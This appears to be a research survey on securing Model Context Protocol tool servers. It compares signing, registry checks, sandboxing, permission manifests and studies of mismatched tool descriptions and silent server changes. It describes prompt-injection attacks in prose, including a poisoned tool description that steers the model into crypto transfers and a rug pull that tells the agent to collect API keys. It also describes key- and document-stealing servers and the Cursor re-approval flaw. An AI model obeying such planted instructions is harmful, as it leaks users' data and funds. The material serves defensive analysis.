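By late 2026, the large catalogs commonly verified publishers but not code. The official MCP registry offers publishers four ways to prove that they own a name, according to its code page on pkg.go.dev. They can log in to GitHub, publish from GitHub's build service, or prove control of a web domain through its DNS records or a file on the site. The registry also checks who owns packages on npm and other stores. For packages on PyPI and NuGet, the store for Microsoft's .NET, it looks for the server's name in the README file, and for container images it looks in a label. The registry does not sign tool descriptions.

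Windows has gone furthest in verifying local servers. In May 2025, Microsoft (2025) announced that servers in the Windows registry of MCP servers would need signed code and could not change their tool definitions while running. When a preview followed in November, Microsoft (2025) promised that each machine's registry would expose only properly packaged and signed components. According to Microsoft's packaging documentation, the usual Windows package format, MSIX, requires a signature whose certificate leads back to an authority the device trusts. Windows hides a server without a package identity from the registry unless the user turns on a setting called "Reduce protections for agent connectors".

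Other hosts on the same machine may be far less strict, because a user can still add a server to a coding assistant's configuration file by hand. Anthropic says Claude Desktop installs local servers from MCPB bundles with one click. The official registry requires a hash for these bundles, and Microsoft's own registry on Windows excludes them by default.

OpenAI has the most detailed process for remote servers, in the plugin directory shared by ChatGPT and OpenAI's coding agent, Codex. Publishers must verify their identity as a person or a business. They also prove that they control the server's domain by placing a token on it, as OpenAI's *Upload and submit your plugin* explains. OpenAI then scans the server, stores its tool definitions, and has people and automated checks review them.

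The scans continue daily after publication. If the developer changes a tool's description, the model still receives the old one until the new one passes automated checks. A new tool stays unavailable until it passes. Users avoid ETDI's repeated prompts but have to trust OpenAI's checks. But tool calls go to the developer's live server. OpenAI's *Remote MCP server review requirements* states that OpenAI keeps the definition but no copy of the implementation, and warns developers that "Server changes take effect before a scan can discover or approve them."

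The table compares the checks on the four questions of provenance, integrity, description-code consistency and confinement.

| Check | Who published it? | Is it unchanged? | Does the description match the code? | What can the code reach? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hash of the package | No answer | Yes, if the expected hash is genuine | No answer | No limit |
| Signature on the package | Whoever holds the key | Yes, since signing | No answer | No limit |
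| Pinned hash | No answer | Yes, since approval | No answer | No limit |
| Build attestation | Source repository and build service | Yes, since the build | No answer, but a reviewer can find the source | No limit |
| Official registry's name check | GitHub account or domain | No answer | No answer | No limit |
| ETDI | Signer of the definition | Definition only | No answer | Declares permissions; enforcing them takes a policy engine |
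| Metere's admission check | Signer who vouches for the server | Signed statement only | No answer | Limits which tools the host calls, not the code |
| TrustDesc | No answer | No answer | Mostly, for open code that is not malicious | No limit |
| OpenAI's directory | Verified person or business | Definition only | Partly, through review and test cases | No limit |

### Objections and replies

The most common objection is that a signature identifies the signer without showing that the code is harmless. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues, 2026) demonstrates this with a signed tool that sends documents to an outside service for text extraction. A hidden routine in the tool keeps a salary sheet from an earlier call and adds it to the request when the user later asks the tool to process an invoice. The host permits the service, but the service has no clearance for salary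 data. With signature checks and a pinned publisher key in place, the tool leaked the data in all three trials. Three trials are few, but the result hardly depends on chance, because the signature covers the hidden routine along with the rest of the code. In a real precedent, maintainer-signed releases of XZ, a widely used compression program, contained a backdoor.

Proponents can answer that signatures are meant for provenance and revocation, which are Microsoft's stated reasons for requiring them. Once someone discovers a leak, hosts can block everything signed with the publisher's key, and a publisher with a verified business identity has more to lose than an anonymous one. Signatures therefore help against repeat offenders and impostors, but they do little for the first victims, who install the tool before anyone has found the leak.

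Another objection is that a description can be signed without being tied to the code, which is why the wallpaper tool passes ETDI's checks. The obvious fix is to sign both together. Bernstein's documentation, for example, provides for a signed manifest that includes a hash of the server's files, so a change to either the description or the files breaks the check. But a description that was false when the publisher signed it would still pass. For open-source servers, generating the description from the code, and using an attestation to confirm that the package came from that code, would further reduce the risk of a mismatch.

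Even a hash of the whole package can miss code that the server runs. *MCP-38* describes a server that loads its main functions from an outside file host each time it starts. An attacker who takes over that host can replace the functions without changing the package or its hash. A verifier could refuse servers that load code this way, but it would first have to recognize them.

Remote servers are the hardest to verify because the user's host cannot hash a program on someone else's machine. OpenAI's rules let developers deploy a server-only fix without a new review if it keeps to the published definitions. Developers need this freedom to repair faults quickly, but a dishonest developer could use it to start copying data. The proponents' best reply is to verify the operator's identity and the definitions, which are visible, and to send the server only data it is allowed to see, though this last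 measure limits the tool instead of verifying it.

People may also be unwilling to accept the burdens of verification. Bhatt and colleagues list the drawbacks of their proposal: keys to manage, added delay, repeated approval prompts, and little benefit until many providers and hosts take part. Short-lived signing spares small developers from guarding a permanent key, and automated review like OpenAI's can replace some of the prompts. Metere leaves MCP's messages unchanged, so adoption can be gradual and hosts that don't support the signed file ignore it. In the open version of Enclawed, a failed check produces only a warning and the connection goes ahead. This keeps existing servers working but gives up the refusal that the verification view requires.

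## The view that every tool should be confined

Signed code can still be malicious, so people who want tools confined assume that any tool may be hostile and limit what it can do, no matter who wrote it.

Their guiding principle is least privilege: a program should get only the access its job requires, not everything its user can reach.

Confining a tool doesn't require anyone to judge its code. It also limits the damage from a server with an accidental bug, or from one whose author unknowingly included a malicious library. Because the operating system enforces the limits, a cleverly worded prompt can't lift them by itself. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) demonstrated these limits on a server written to steal a private SSH key, a file that lets its holder log in to other machines. Without a sandbox, the server read the key and sent it out. With the network blocked, it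 read the key but couldn't send it. In a full sandbox, it couldn't read the key at all.

The strictest version of this view, in *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025), would require hosts to run every MCP server in a container or a virtual machine. Servers would have read-only access to files by default, could reach only approved network addresses, and would receive no credentials from the host.

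### Ways to confine a server

One option is to run the server under a different account. Microsoft says a preview feature of Windows runs servers from the system's own registry in a separate session as an "agent" user. They can't open the user's files or credentials without permission, but they can still reach the whole internet. MCPB bundles can't run this way yet.

A container gives a program its own view of files, processes and the network. As *Abstraction of Trusted Execution Environments as the Missing Layer* (2025) explains, containers share the host's Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, while a virtual machine needs its own full operating system. Docker, a maker of container software, offers a gateway that runs MCP servers in containers with restricted privileges and network access. A careless setting can undo this protection. In an example from *MCP-38*, a server that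 can reach Docker's control socket starts a second container with the host's file system attached.

WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs that run inside a small virtual machine. Under WASI, the interface that connects them to the rest of the computer, they start with no outside access. Microsoft's *Introducing Wassette* (2025) presents a way to run MCP tools in this format and argues that third-party tools on a user's own machine need such isolation. Microsoft's *Frequently Asked Questions (FAQ)* concedes that developers must rewrite their existing servers. *MCP-SandboxScan* (2026) describes a system that tests MCP tools in WebAssembly where possible, and recommends an operating-system sandbox for other untrusted servers.

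An operating-system sandbox restricts a program without changing the program's code. *Sandlock* (2026) combines two Linux features to do this and needs no administrator rights. Landlock sets in advance which files and network ports the program may use. Seccomp lets a supervisor check the program's system calls (its requests to the kernel) as they happen, so the supervisor can allow some network addresses and block others.

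The *MCP configuration reference* for VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, describes a sandbox for local servers. It works only on macOS and Linux, and users have to switch it on for each server. They can list the folders a server may write to and the domains it may contact. They can restrict reading only by listing what is forbidden, so a folder they forget presumably stays readable. According to Anthropic, Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers shell commands but not MCP servers.

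Sandboxes don't limit what a server can do with an access token, because the token takes effect on another system, such as GitHub's machines for a GitHub token. Short-lived tokens with narrow permissions reduce this risk, since a stolen one soon stops working and gives access to only part of an account. Docker's gateway fetches credentials from a company's secret store when a tool runs, which keeps long-lived credentials out of configuration files. *MCPGuard* (2025) describes another framework that issues credentials just before use and limits their scope.

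### A permission manifest for the weather server

AgentBound combines a container with a permission manifest, a list of the kinds of access that a server needs. Bühler and colleagues based its vocabulary on Android, where apps declare whether they use the camera or the internet. For the weather server, a simplified version might look like this:

```jsonc
// The author declares the kind of access the server needs
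{
  "description": "Gets current weather information for a location",
  "capabilities": ["mcp.ac.network.client"]
}

// The user approves the exact address when the server runs
{ "mcp.ac.network.client": "https://api.weather.example" }
```

The server gets no file access because the manifest doesn't list any. If the agent later requests a permission the manifest doesn't cover, AgentBound aborts the run.

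To enforce the manifest, AgentBound starts a Docker container, installs the package, looks up the IP address of the approved host and then blocks all other traffic. Code that runs during installation would therefore still have unrestricted network access, but this container would hold none of the user's files.

If the weather server contains hidden code that copies documents at launch, that code finds no documents in the container and cannot connect to the attacker's own machine. Confinement therefore stops the theft that worried defenders of verification, even though nobody has inspected the code.

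The hidden code still receives everything the host passes as arguments. Normally this is a place name, although a few months of place names can reveal where a user lives and travels. The tool's author could collect more by adding an input called "reason for request" to the schema. The model might fill it in with details from the conversation, such as a medical appointment or a confidential client meeting. The server could then include this text in its request to the weather service, and the firewall would allow the request because the service's address is on the list.

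A dishonest author who runs the weather service gets all of the text. If a national weather office runs it, the text still goes to an organization that shouldn't have it, but the author may have no way to retrieve it.

Aun and colleagues measured this weakness with 91 malicious versions of a note-reading tool, generated with a language model. A list of permitted addresses stopped all 71 versions that sent data to the attacker's own host, but none of the 20 that sent it to a permitted address. The researchers chose this mix, so the overall rate of 78% does not show how often such a list would work against real attackers.

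Like the signed tool that leaked a salary sheet, the server can also keep data from one call and send it during a later one. It could also put instructions for the model in its forecasts. *Unsafe by Flow* (2026) warns that text from a tool can re-enter prompts and later tool calls, and recommends sandboxing as only one of several measures to reduce the risk.

### How much AgentBound stopped

Bühler and colleagues tested AgentBound on 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections. It stopped the attacks on eight of them and failed on five. The remaining server combined several attacks, and AgentBound could stop only some of them. It also stopped the server that steals SSH keys, for a total of nine out of 15.

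One of the attacks AgentBound stopped came from a Google Maps server whose hidden code replaced Google's address with the attacker's. Another was a rug pull, in which a weather tool's description changed after the third call to include instructions for the agent to collect API keys from a configuration file. The five attacks it failed to stop either stayed within the server's permissions or affected only the model. For example, AgentBound couldn't stop an attacker from inserting commands into a WeChat server's database queries, because the server needs its database to work.

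The sample is small. The researchers wrote or checked the manifests, and a single tester approved the permissions. The results therefore indicate what AgentBound can do with correct permissions, but ordinary users may choose worse ones.

Writing a correct manifest takes some effort, so the researchers had a language model draft manifests for 296 popular servers. They sent 96 of the drafts to the servers' developers, most of whom never replied. Those who did accepted 17 and rejected four, so the paper's 80.9% accuracy figure is based on only 21 verdicts. The researchers also wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, and the model's drafts were identical to theirs for 28. Most of the model's mistakes were missing permissions, which would break a server feature but wouldn't give hidden code more access.

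AgentBound added roughly 90 to 430 milliseconds to a server's start-up time, not counting the package download, and less than a millisecond on average to operations such as reading a file. Users would hardly notice these delays next to the time a model takes to answer. *My Credentials, Please* (2026) also found that isolating the server process enforced least privilege without disrupting the tools' normal functions, though this finding rests on only three cases.

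### The NSA's guidance

The US National Security Agency (NSA) supported confinement in its May 2026 guidance for organizations, *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*. The guidance advises treating any tool execution through MCP as a potentially high-risk action. It recommends isolating each tool with the operating system's own security features, such as AppContainers on Windows or seccomp, AppArmor and SELinux on Linux. It also recommends explicitly denying each server access at run time to files and internal networks it doesn't need.

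The NSA also wants organizations to group tools by the sensitivity of the data they handle. A weather tool belongs with public data, while tools that handle health or financial records need separate, controlled access. For private data, the agency prefers a local server to a remote one. It recommends sending outgoing traffic through a filtering proxy that permits only specific web addresses and access methods. Such a proxy is more precise than AgentBound's firewall, which permits or blocks a whole IP address.

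One of its examples is a simple weather server that somebody deploys without restrictions and later reuses to process sensitive information about people or assets at a location. Permissions that suited the original job may be too broad for the new one, so organizations need to review them when a tool's use changes.

The NSA criticizes the protocol itself for how it handles permissions. MCP has no way for a client and server to exchange role-based permissions when they connect, and the version the agency reviewed recommends tokens that expire but doesn't require them. Docker's *The Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) had also warned that an agent allowed to connect to a server may call every tool the server offers. The NSA's example is the GitHub server, which can receive blanket access to a user's repositories. A malicious or compromised tool could then copy private code into a public repository.

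The guidance includes no tests of these measures, and some of them suit a large organization better than a developer working alone, who is unlikely to run a filtering proxy.

### Useful tools and broad permissions

The weather server is easy to confine because it needs little access. Bühler and colleagues examined 296 servers, and the generated manifests list outgoing network access for 83.1% of them and reading files for 74.1%. At least 57% must therefore have both, and a program with both can steal documents. Supporters of confinement reply that a server rarely needs every file or every address. An owner can limit a documentation tool to one project folder and one website, which protects files outside that folder but not the project itself.

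Aun and colleagues propose a way to protect data that a tool does need. Their system keeps a process of the tool that never receives user data. For each call, it makes temporary copies of this process, gives each copy only the data that its destination may receive, and then discards the copies. In their example of the salary sheet and the invoice, the copy that contacts the text-extraction service never receives the salary sheet, so hidden code cannot add the sheet's contents to the request.

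Data leaked in 114 of 153 attack runs when the host relied on signatures and a pinned key. Confinement, combined with sensitivity labels on the tools' replies, reduced this to 51, and the temporary copies reduced it to zero. A call that needed one copy took 10 to 49 milliseconds. But somebody has to label the data and decide which destinations may receive it. A bank may already have such rules, but few people have them for the files on their own laptop. The system also can't copy a remote server, so it has to treat that server's replies as if they contained the most sensitive data the server has received.

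Users may also grant more access than a tool needs, especially if the system offers no narrower option. In the Windows preview, permission to read user files applies to the host, not to a single server. If a user grants it for a photo organizer, a weather server in the same host can read the files too. Manifests can help by setting a low limit on access before the user sees any request. One developer who reviewed a draft manifest for Bühler and colleagues wanted to narrow its permissions further, so that the server could read only the environment variables it uses.

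A sandbox can also lead a host to relax other protections. VS Code automatically approves tool calls from a sandboxed server, on the grounds that the server runs in a controlled environment. This is reasonable for a call that might damage files. But it removes the user's chance to notice private information in a call, such as a medical appointment mentioned in the "reason for request" sent to a weather service.

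### When a confined server misuses a trusted one

A sandbox can't contain a server's description, because the host passes it to the model. In one attack that AgentBound failed to stop, a server that tells the time had a description instructing the model to send cryptocurrency transfers through a certain address. The model then called a separate, legitimate wallet tool, which had permission to make the transfer. The WhatsApp attack that Willison described, which the NSA also cites, works the same way.

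Supporters of this view reply that the host should confine trusted servers as well. Bühler and colleagues give the example of an agent that writes documentation using one server for files and another for web pages. A poisoned tool description contains instructions to overwrite each file and send its contents to an attacker's website. Confinement blocks both steps, because the file server can only read the source code and the web server can only contact the documentation site. It works when the attacker wants something outside the trusted tool's normal job, but it can't protect a wallet tool, whose job is to transfer money.

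Separating tools by sensitivity, as the NSA recommends, would help in both cases. If the host never offers the time server and the wallet in the same conversation, the time server's description can't influence a transfer. The user gives up some convenience, since MCP's appeal is that one assistant can use many tools together. Separation also has to cover shared files. *My Credentials, Please* describes how one tool can write an attacker's text to a file that a second tool later reads, even if each stays within its own limits.

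A host or proxy can also check each call before it reaches a server. Microsoft's *Ignite 2025 furthering Windows as the premier platform for developers* (2025) describes a Windows proxy that enforces permissions and logs every interaction. Such checks can be fast. In *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026), a simple access list added at most 0.1 milliseconds to a file copy that took about 2.3 milliseconds. In the same tests, neither per-call checks nor handles, which let a caller refer to data without seeing it, stopped a caller from sending a secret it already knew.

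## Whether descriptions match the code, at first and after updates

Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) found in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* that about one tool in ten has a description that doesn't match its code. Most of these mismatches look like careless documentation, though a few conceal an upload or a missing safety step. A description that is accurate when the user approves a tool can also become wrong later, and the user often gets no warning.

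### Seven kinds of mismatch

Shi and colleagues treat a tool as a pair, T = (D, C), where D is the description that the model sees and C is the code. On each side they look at the tool's functions (Φ), meaning the work it does for the user, and at its effects on its surroundings (Ψ), such as changed files or data sent elsewhere. "Claim" marks what the description leads a reader to expect, and "act" marks what the code does. A tool has a description-code inconsistency (DCI) if

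$$\mathrm{DCI}(T) := (\Phi_{\text{claim}} \neq \Phi_{\text{act}}) \lor (\Psi_{\text{act}} \nsubseteq \Psi_{\text{claim}})$$

A tool is inconsistent if its functions differ from the ones its description claims, or if it has an effect that the description leaves out. Both missing and extra functions count. A described effect that never happens, such as writing a log file, doesn't count, because nothing happens that the user didn't expect.

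The definition covers seven kinds of mismatch, which Shi and colleagues illustrate with a tool for finding files.

| Kind | Description | What the code does |
|---|---|---|
| Undeclared function | Search local files by name | Also searches cloud storage |
| Overclaimed function | Search local and cloud files by name | Searches only local files |
| Misclaimed function | Search local files by name | Deletes the file |
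| Ambiguous function | Process local files | Searches by name |
| Resource overconsumption | Search local files by name | Builds an index of the whole disk first |
| State mutation | Search local files by name | Gives every user of the machine full access to the folder |
| Data leakage | Search local files by name | Also uploads the search term to a remote server |

A weather server that secretly copies the user's documents would count as data leakage. But the definition also covers ordinary product features. In another of the paper's examples, a weather tool stores each city the user asks about, updates a user profile and sends the query to an analytics service. The developer may only want to offer better recommendations later, but the tool is still inconsistent because nothing in its description shows the user or the model that it keeps a history.

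Some of the boundaries are a matter of judgment. Heavy resource use counts only above a threshold, which reviewers could set differently. The undeclared cloud search in the table sends the search term off the machine, so it could also count as data leakage.

### How DCIChecker compares a description with code

Shi and colleagues built a program called DCIChecker to apply the definition to thousands of tools. It reads source code without running it, in these steps:

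1. Find where the program registers a tool, and record the name, schema and text that a model would receive.
2. Start from the function that handles calls to the tool, and follow its calls to other functions in the same project, up to three levels deep.
3. List the sensitive operations in this code, such as network requests, file deletions and reads of environment variables, which often hold passwords or keys. Include fixed details such as web addresses.
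4. Give the description and the collected code to a language model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, with two opposed prompts. One asks it to check that the two are consistent, and the other asks it to find inconsistencies.
5. Accept the answer if both prompts produce the same label, including the same kind of mismatch. Otherwise, have the model weigh both explanations against the code and decide.

The procedure uses opposed prompts because language models' answers tend to follow a question's framing. To measure this, the researchers labeled 400 real tools by hand. Two of them judged each tool independently and a third settled disagreements, which gave 197 inconsistent tools and 203 consistent ones. The prompt about consistency found only 93 of the 197 inconsistent tools. The prompt about inconsistency found all of them but also wrongly flagged 53 consistent tools. The full procedure found 192 and wrongly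 flagged eight, using the deciding step for 153 of the 400 tools.

This gives DCIChecker a precision of 96% (the share of its reports that are correct) and a recall of 97.5% (the share of inconsistent tools that it finds). Recall is probably lower in ordinary use, because the researchers drew half of their sample from tools that DCIChecker had flagged, while in the full collection it flagged only about one in nine of the tools it could check. Five of the 200 sampled tools that it had passed were inconsistent. At that rate, it would have missed about 380 of the 15,123 tools it passed in the full collection, which would put its recall at roughly 83%. Five errors are too few for a precise estimate, but they suggest that the published count of inconsistent tools is somewhat low.

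Like TrustDesc, DCIChecker starts from the function that handles a call, so it would miss code that copies the user's files when the server launches.

### One tool in ten, one server in three

Shi and colleagues ran DCIChecker on 2,214 servers written in Python, the most common language for MCP servers, and extracted 19,200 tools. They couldn't check 2,170 of these tools because they had no descriptive text. One likely reason for the missing text is that the Python development kit can take a tool's description from a comment in the code, so a developer who leaves out the comment publishes a tool without a description.

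DCIChecker found 1,907 inconsistent tools, which is 9.93% of all the tools and 11.2% of those with a description to check. It found at least one inconsistent tool in 775 servers (35%).

Overclaiming was the most common kind of mismatch, at 35.4% of the cases. About three quarters of the cases were mismatched functions of some kind, and the rest were undeclared side effects. An undeclared side effect was therefore the main fault in about 2.5% of all tools, and these tools are the most likely to surprise a user who only wanted the described function.

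A developer usually connects several servers. If each has a 35% chance of containing an inconsistent tool, the chance that all five servers in a random selection are free of them is 0.65 multiplied by itself five times, or about 12%. The chance of at least one inconsistent tool is therefore

$$1 - 0.65^5 \approx 0.88$$

or about 88%. This assumes that the five servers are independent random draws from servers like those in the study. Real choices are neither random nor independent. A careful developer may pick better-maintained servers, while one who installs several from the same publisher may get the same faults in all of them. The calculation also counts a server with one bad tool among 30 that the agent never calls. For five tools drawn at random, the chance that at least one is inconsistent is about 41%.

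Servers with three or more inconsistent tools made up only 8.27% of the total but contained 60.3% of the cases of inconsistency. A registry could therefore remove much of the problem by getting fewer than 200 developers to correct their descriptions.

### Two tools that a user might regret

One of the tools has the description "Convert local PDF file to Markdown using OCR." OCR (optical character recognition) turns an image of a page into text, and a laptop can do this without an internet connection. This tool instead uploads the whole PDF to an outside service.

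Shi and colleagues read the description as a claim that the conversion happens locally. "Local" could also mean only that the file starts out on the user's disk. Either way, the description doesn't mention the upload. If a lawyer asked an agent to convert a confidential contract, the model would have no reason to warn the lawyer that the tool would upload it.

Another tool submits orders to the MAX exchange. According to its description, "A confirmation prompt requires explicit user approval before execution." The code has no such prompt and submits the order immediately. The host might still ask for permission before the call, but a user who believes the tool will ask may have let the host run it automatically, in which case the order is submitted without the user's approval.

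Other cases would mostly waste the user's time. One tool is described as providing local weather forecasts, but its code queries exchange rates. Another, described as "Process some data", only inserts a number and a name into a fixed sentence.

### MCPDiff and its different yardstick

Earlier in 2026, Li, Ma and colleagues used a program called MCPDiff to examine 10,240 servers (*Don't believe everything you read*, 2026). Their headline figure of about 13% measures something different from DCIChecker's 9.93%.

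MCPDiff uses a language model to summarize the functions in a server's code and the project's documentation, such as its README file. It then converts both sets of summaries into vectors (lists of numbers that are similar when the texts have similar meanings) and calculates what share of the code's features the documentation covers. Coverage was complete for 5,303 servers and between 80% and 100% for another 3,544. The 13% consists of 1,079 servers with coverage between 40% and 80% and 314 with lower coverage.

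The figure applies to whole servers, not individual tools. MCPDiff also ignores overclaiming, on the reasoning that a missing feature hides nothing from the user, so it leaves out the most common kind of mismatch in DCIChecker's results. And a README isn't the description that the model reads. In one of the paper's cases, the documentation of longport-mcp, a server for a securities trading service, omits `submit_order` and `cancel_order`. This could mislead a person who reads it before installing the server, but if the server offers these functions as tools, the model will find their names in the tool list.

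Another case, in the mcpx-py framework for building MCP software, may be less serious than it appears. The framework's code contains an undocumented function that can end any process and all the processes it started. Li and colleagues warn that an attacker could use it to stop critical services. But a framework that launches other programs ordinarily needs to stop them, and a helper function in its code may never be available to an agent as a tool.

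A server's popularity did not reliably indicate the quality of its documentation. The worst mismatches appeared in 3.5% of servers with fewer than ten GitHub stars and in none of the 19 servers with at least 10,000. But descriptions matched the code completely for 53.5% of servers in the least popular group, compared with 29.1% of those with 1,000 to 9,999 stars. Larger projects probably have more functions to document and so more chances to leave one out.

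Shi and colleagues rebuilt MCPDiff from its published description and tested it on their hand-labeled tools. It found 90 of the 197 inconsistent ones. This comparison favors DCIChecker, because 192 of those were in the sample only because DCIChecker had flagged them.

### Most mismatches are not attacks

Shi and colleagues don't accuse any developer of malice, and their results suggest that most mismatches have ordinary causes, such as developers describing features they plan to add or changing the code without updating the description. An attacker would have little reason to advertise a cloud search that doesn't exist. On servers with several inconsistent tools, about two thirds of those tools had the server's most common kind of mismatch, as one would expect if developers reuse the same template or documentation habits across tools.

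Many developers write very little in their tool descriptions. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) found that, of 1,856 tools, 65% had descriptions that stated only their basic function and 7% had descriptions that included security information. A one-line description leaves out most side effects, even when the developer isn't trying to hide them.

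The protocol's yes-or-no hints could fill some of this gap, but few developers use them informatively. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (2026) counts 98,291 tools on remote servers in the official registry, 65.8% of which had the hint about destructive actions. That hint applies only to tools that can change data, yet many of the tools that had it were also marked read-only. Only 12.9% of all the tools had hints that usefully indicated whether they might destroy something.

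A mismatch does the same harm whether it is deliberate or accidental. The PDF reaches the outside service even if the developer just forgot to mention it. But the right remedy depends on the cause. Better documentation tools, and checks like DCIChecker at publication, would help honest developers who make mistakes. Finding deliberately malicious code is a separate task for scanners, and 9.93% is not an estimate of how common such code is.

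### When an approved tool changes

In a rug pull, an approved tool changes for the worse. *MCP-38* lists several changes that would be harder for a user to see than a replaced description. The server's operator may direct requests to a different machine, or add a backdoor to the code without changing the tool's interface. A library that the server depends on may become malicious. The changes may also come in small steps, none of which looks alarming alone.

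### The approval that Cursor remembered by name

The coding assistant Cursor had a flaw that let a user's approval remain valid after the thing they had approved changed. Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu (2025) reported the flaw for the security company Check Point in *CVE-2025-54136*, whose title is the flaw's CVE number.

Cursor can read its list of MCP servers from a file in the project folder. Teams often share this folder through a Git repository, so a change by one member reaches everyone else at the next update. Cursor asked each user to approve a server the first time it appeared in the file, but recorded the approval under the server's name alone. The difference between that rule and a safer one fits in a few lines of simplified code:

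```python
# Before version 1.3: has the user approved a server with this name?
may_run = entry.name in approved_names

# A safer rule: has the user approved this exact entry?
may_run = fingerprint(entry.name, entry.command, entry.args) in approved_entries
```

An attacker who could edit the shared file would first add a server with a harmless command. A colleague would open the project and approve the server. The attacker could then replace the command but keep the server's name. Cursor would run the new command on the colleague's machine every time the colleague opened the project, without asking again.

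According to MITRE's official CVE entry, *Cursor's Modification of MCP Server Definitions Bypasses Manual Re-approvals* (2025), the attacker must already be able to write to the repository's active branches or to files on the victim's machine. Still, many people can write to a typical company repository, and an attacker who steals one of their passwords gets the same access. The entry rates the flaw's severity at 7.2 out of 10. In August 2025, it listed no known exploitation.

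The flaw undermines the view that trust is decided at installation, because the user did everything required at that point. Cursor displayed a server and the user approved it, but the approval then covered a command the user had never seen. Comparing the description with the code would not have helped, since the new command didn't have to start an MCP server.

Check Point reported the flaw on 16 July 2025, and Cursor released version 1.3 on 29 July. Charikov and colleagues found that any change to an entry, even an added space, now triggers a new request for approval. That fixes the flaw, but the program an entry launches can still change while the entry stays the same. If the entry runs a script, for example, somebody can edit the script.

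Other coding agents have since had similar faults. *Coding-Agenten* (Cornelißen, 2026) describes five security advisories from one week in October 2026, all about products whose approval step checked something other than what ran.

### A census of changes in the official registry

Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, measured how often servers change under a fixed name. In August 2026 he downloaded the whole official registry, which held 21,643 servers and 72,606 version records. For the 8,900 servers with more than one version, he compared each version's short registry summary, packages to install, and any remote server addresses with those of the next version.

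At least one of these had changed for 4,547 servers, or 51.1%. Kraishan calls a change silent if the names and identifiers stay the same but the meaning or destination changes. 40.6% of the servers had changed silently. The most worrying group is the 370 servers (4.2%) that moved a remote address to a different host. A user who knows the server only by name could end up sending data to a new destination.

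These percentages apply only to servers with several versions. Across the whole registry, 21% of servers had changed and 1.7% had moved to another host. Silent changes are also often trivial, because any edit to the registry summary counts as one, even a spelling correction. About nine in ten servers with a silent change had at least one edit to this summary.

Kraishan expects that most of the 370 moves were routine, such as a company changing its hosting provider, and he doesn't claim that any was malicious. He is concerned that neither the registry nor the host can distinguish a routine move from a takeover. Existing users will follow the server to its new location if their host looks up the name again, but a host that copied the old address into its configuration will keep using that address.

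Among servers that changed, the median time to the first change was zero days. Kraishan concludes that a typical review at installation describes a server that had already changed the same day. This goes too far, because many publishers probably correct mistakes in a new listing within hours, before anyone has installed the server. The quickest changes are therefore weak evidence about servers that people have used for months.

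However, Bharti (2026), in *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly*, followed the same registry for 89 days and found that three quarters of the servers never changed their entry. The most active 5% made 61% of all the changes. Only 11.9% of servers changed anything in their entry within 30 days, and 3.3% changed the summary. New servers changed most often in their first week, which is consistent with publishers correcting new listings.

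The two sets of figures are compatible because Kraishan looked at the full history of servers that had released several versions, while Bharti followed all servers for a limited time. In Bharti's data, about 1.5% of servers changed their entry on a median day. If each day's changes fell on servers at random, almost 36% would have changed within a month, but only a third as many did because the same servers changed repeatedly.

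In Kraishan's data, servers with silent changes had almost three times the odds of a serious alert from his security scanner. He suggests that poorly managed projects may have both problems. Size could be another explanation, since servers with more code set off more alerts and may also need more updates.

Neither researcher could count the rug pulls that MCP users fear most, in which a server changes the tool definitions that the model reads. The registry's summary of a server, which is limited to 100 characters, is separate from the tool descriptions given to the model. None of the 72,606 version records include tool definitions, because the registry has no place for them. A server could therefore add an instruction to attach private files to every request without changing its registry entry. Kraishan recommends that the registry record tool definitions for each version, and that hosts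 ask users for consent again when a server moves to another address.

### What pinning would have caught

Pinning detects changes from what the user approved, so its value depends on what the user pins. The table shows which of the changes above each of three kinds of pin would detect.

| Change | Pinned configuration entry | Pinned package hash | Pinned tool description |
|---|---|---|---|
| A colleague swaps the launch command, as in Cursor | Caught | Missed if the new command bypasses the package | Too late, because the command has run |
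| The publisher releases a malicious new version | Missed if the entry asks for the latest version | Caught | Missed unless the text changes |
| A reinstallation brings in a different library | Missed | Caught only if the pin covers libraries | Missed unless the text changes |
| A remote server moves to another host | Caught | No package to pin | Missed unless the text changes |
| A remote operator changes the code at the same address | Missed | No package to pin | Missed unless the text changes |
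| The description was wrong from the start | Missed | Missed | Missed |

A host can instead pin the publisher's key, which is a looser check than pinning a hash. In the signed-release system that Aun and colleagues examined, the host pins the key once and then accepts every later release with a valid signature from it. This blocks updates from strangers, but a publisher who turns malicious, or someone who steals the key, can still deliver a rug pull. A pinned hash would block either one's update until the user approves the new release.

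The row about libraries comes from an experiment in *ProbeID*. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) installed 16 published servers at exact versions and recorded how 59 of their tools answered a set of harmless requests. They repeated the requests 11 times over 11 weeks. Seven tools changed their answers by more than their usual variation, although every server still had the same version number.

Three of the seven tools belonged to a weather server, whose answers should change with the weather. A fourth recommends pages from Amazon's cloud documentation. Its answers drifted steadily from the originals, and after 55 days the difference had reached the maximum on the researchers' scale. The change came from the documentation service behind the tool, which pinning the local package's version doesn't control.

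The other three changed when the researchers reinstalled some servers at the same versions. The servers' development kit accepts a range of versions of an input-checking library, and the installer had picked a different one. Only the wording of error messages changed, and Chen and colleagues found no sign of malice in any of the seven cases. But a malicious version of a library could be installed in the same way. To prevent this, the pin has to cover every library the server installs, as in the releases Aun and colleagues describe, where the hash identifies the code and its dependencies together.

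Chen and colleagues propose checking behavior as well. When a user approves a tool, their system, ProbeID, records the tool's answers to up to 512 test inputs. Before a later use, it sends test inputs again and refuses the tool if the answers differ too much. In one experiment, the researchers replaced four servers with altered versions that had identical descriptions. An agent without ProbeID received at least one wrong value in 15 of 16 tasks. With ProbeID, this fell to nine. The benchmark scored every task as a success in both cases, so its scores did not reveal the wrong values.

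ProbeID works only if the test inputs reach the change. Suppose an altered tool gives different answers for a fraction φ of all inputs. The chance that at least one of m random tests reveals a difference is

$$1 - (1 - \varphi)^m$$

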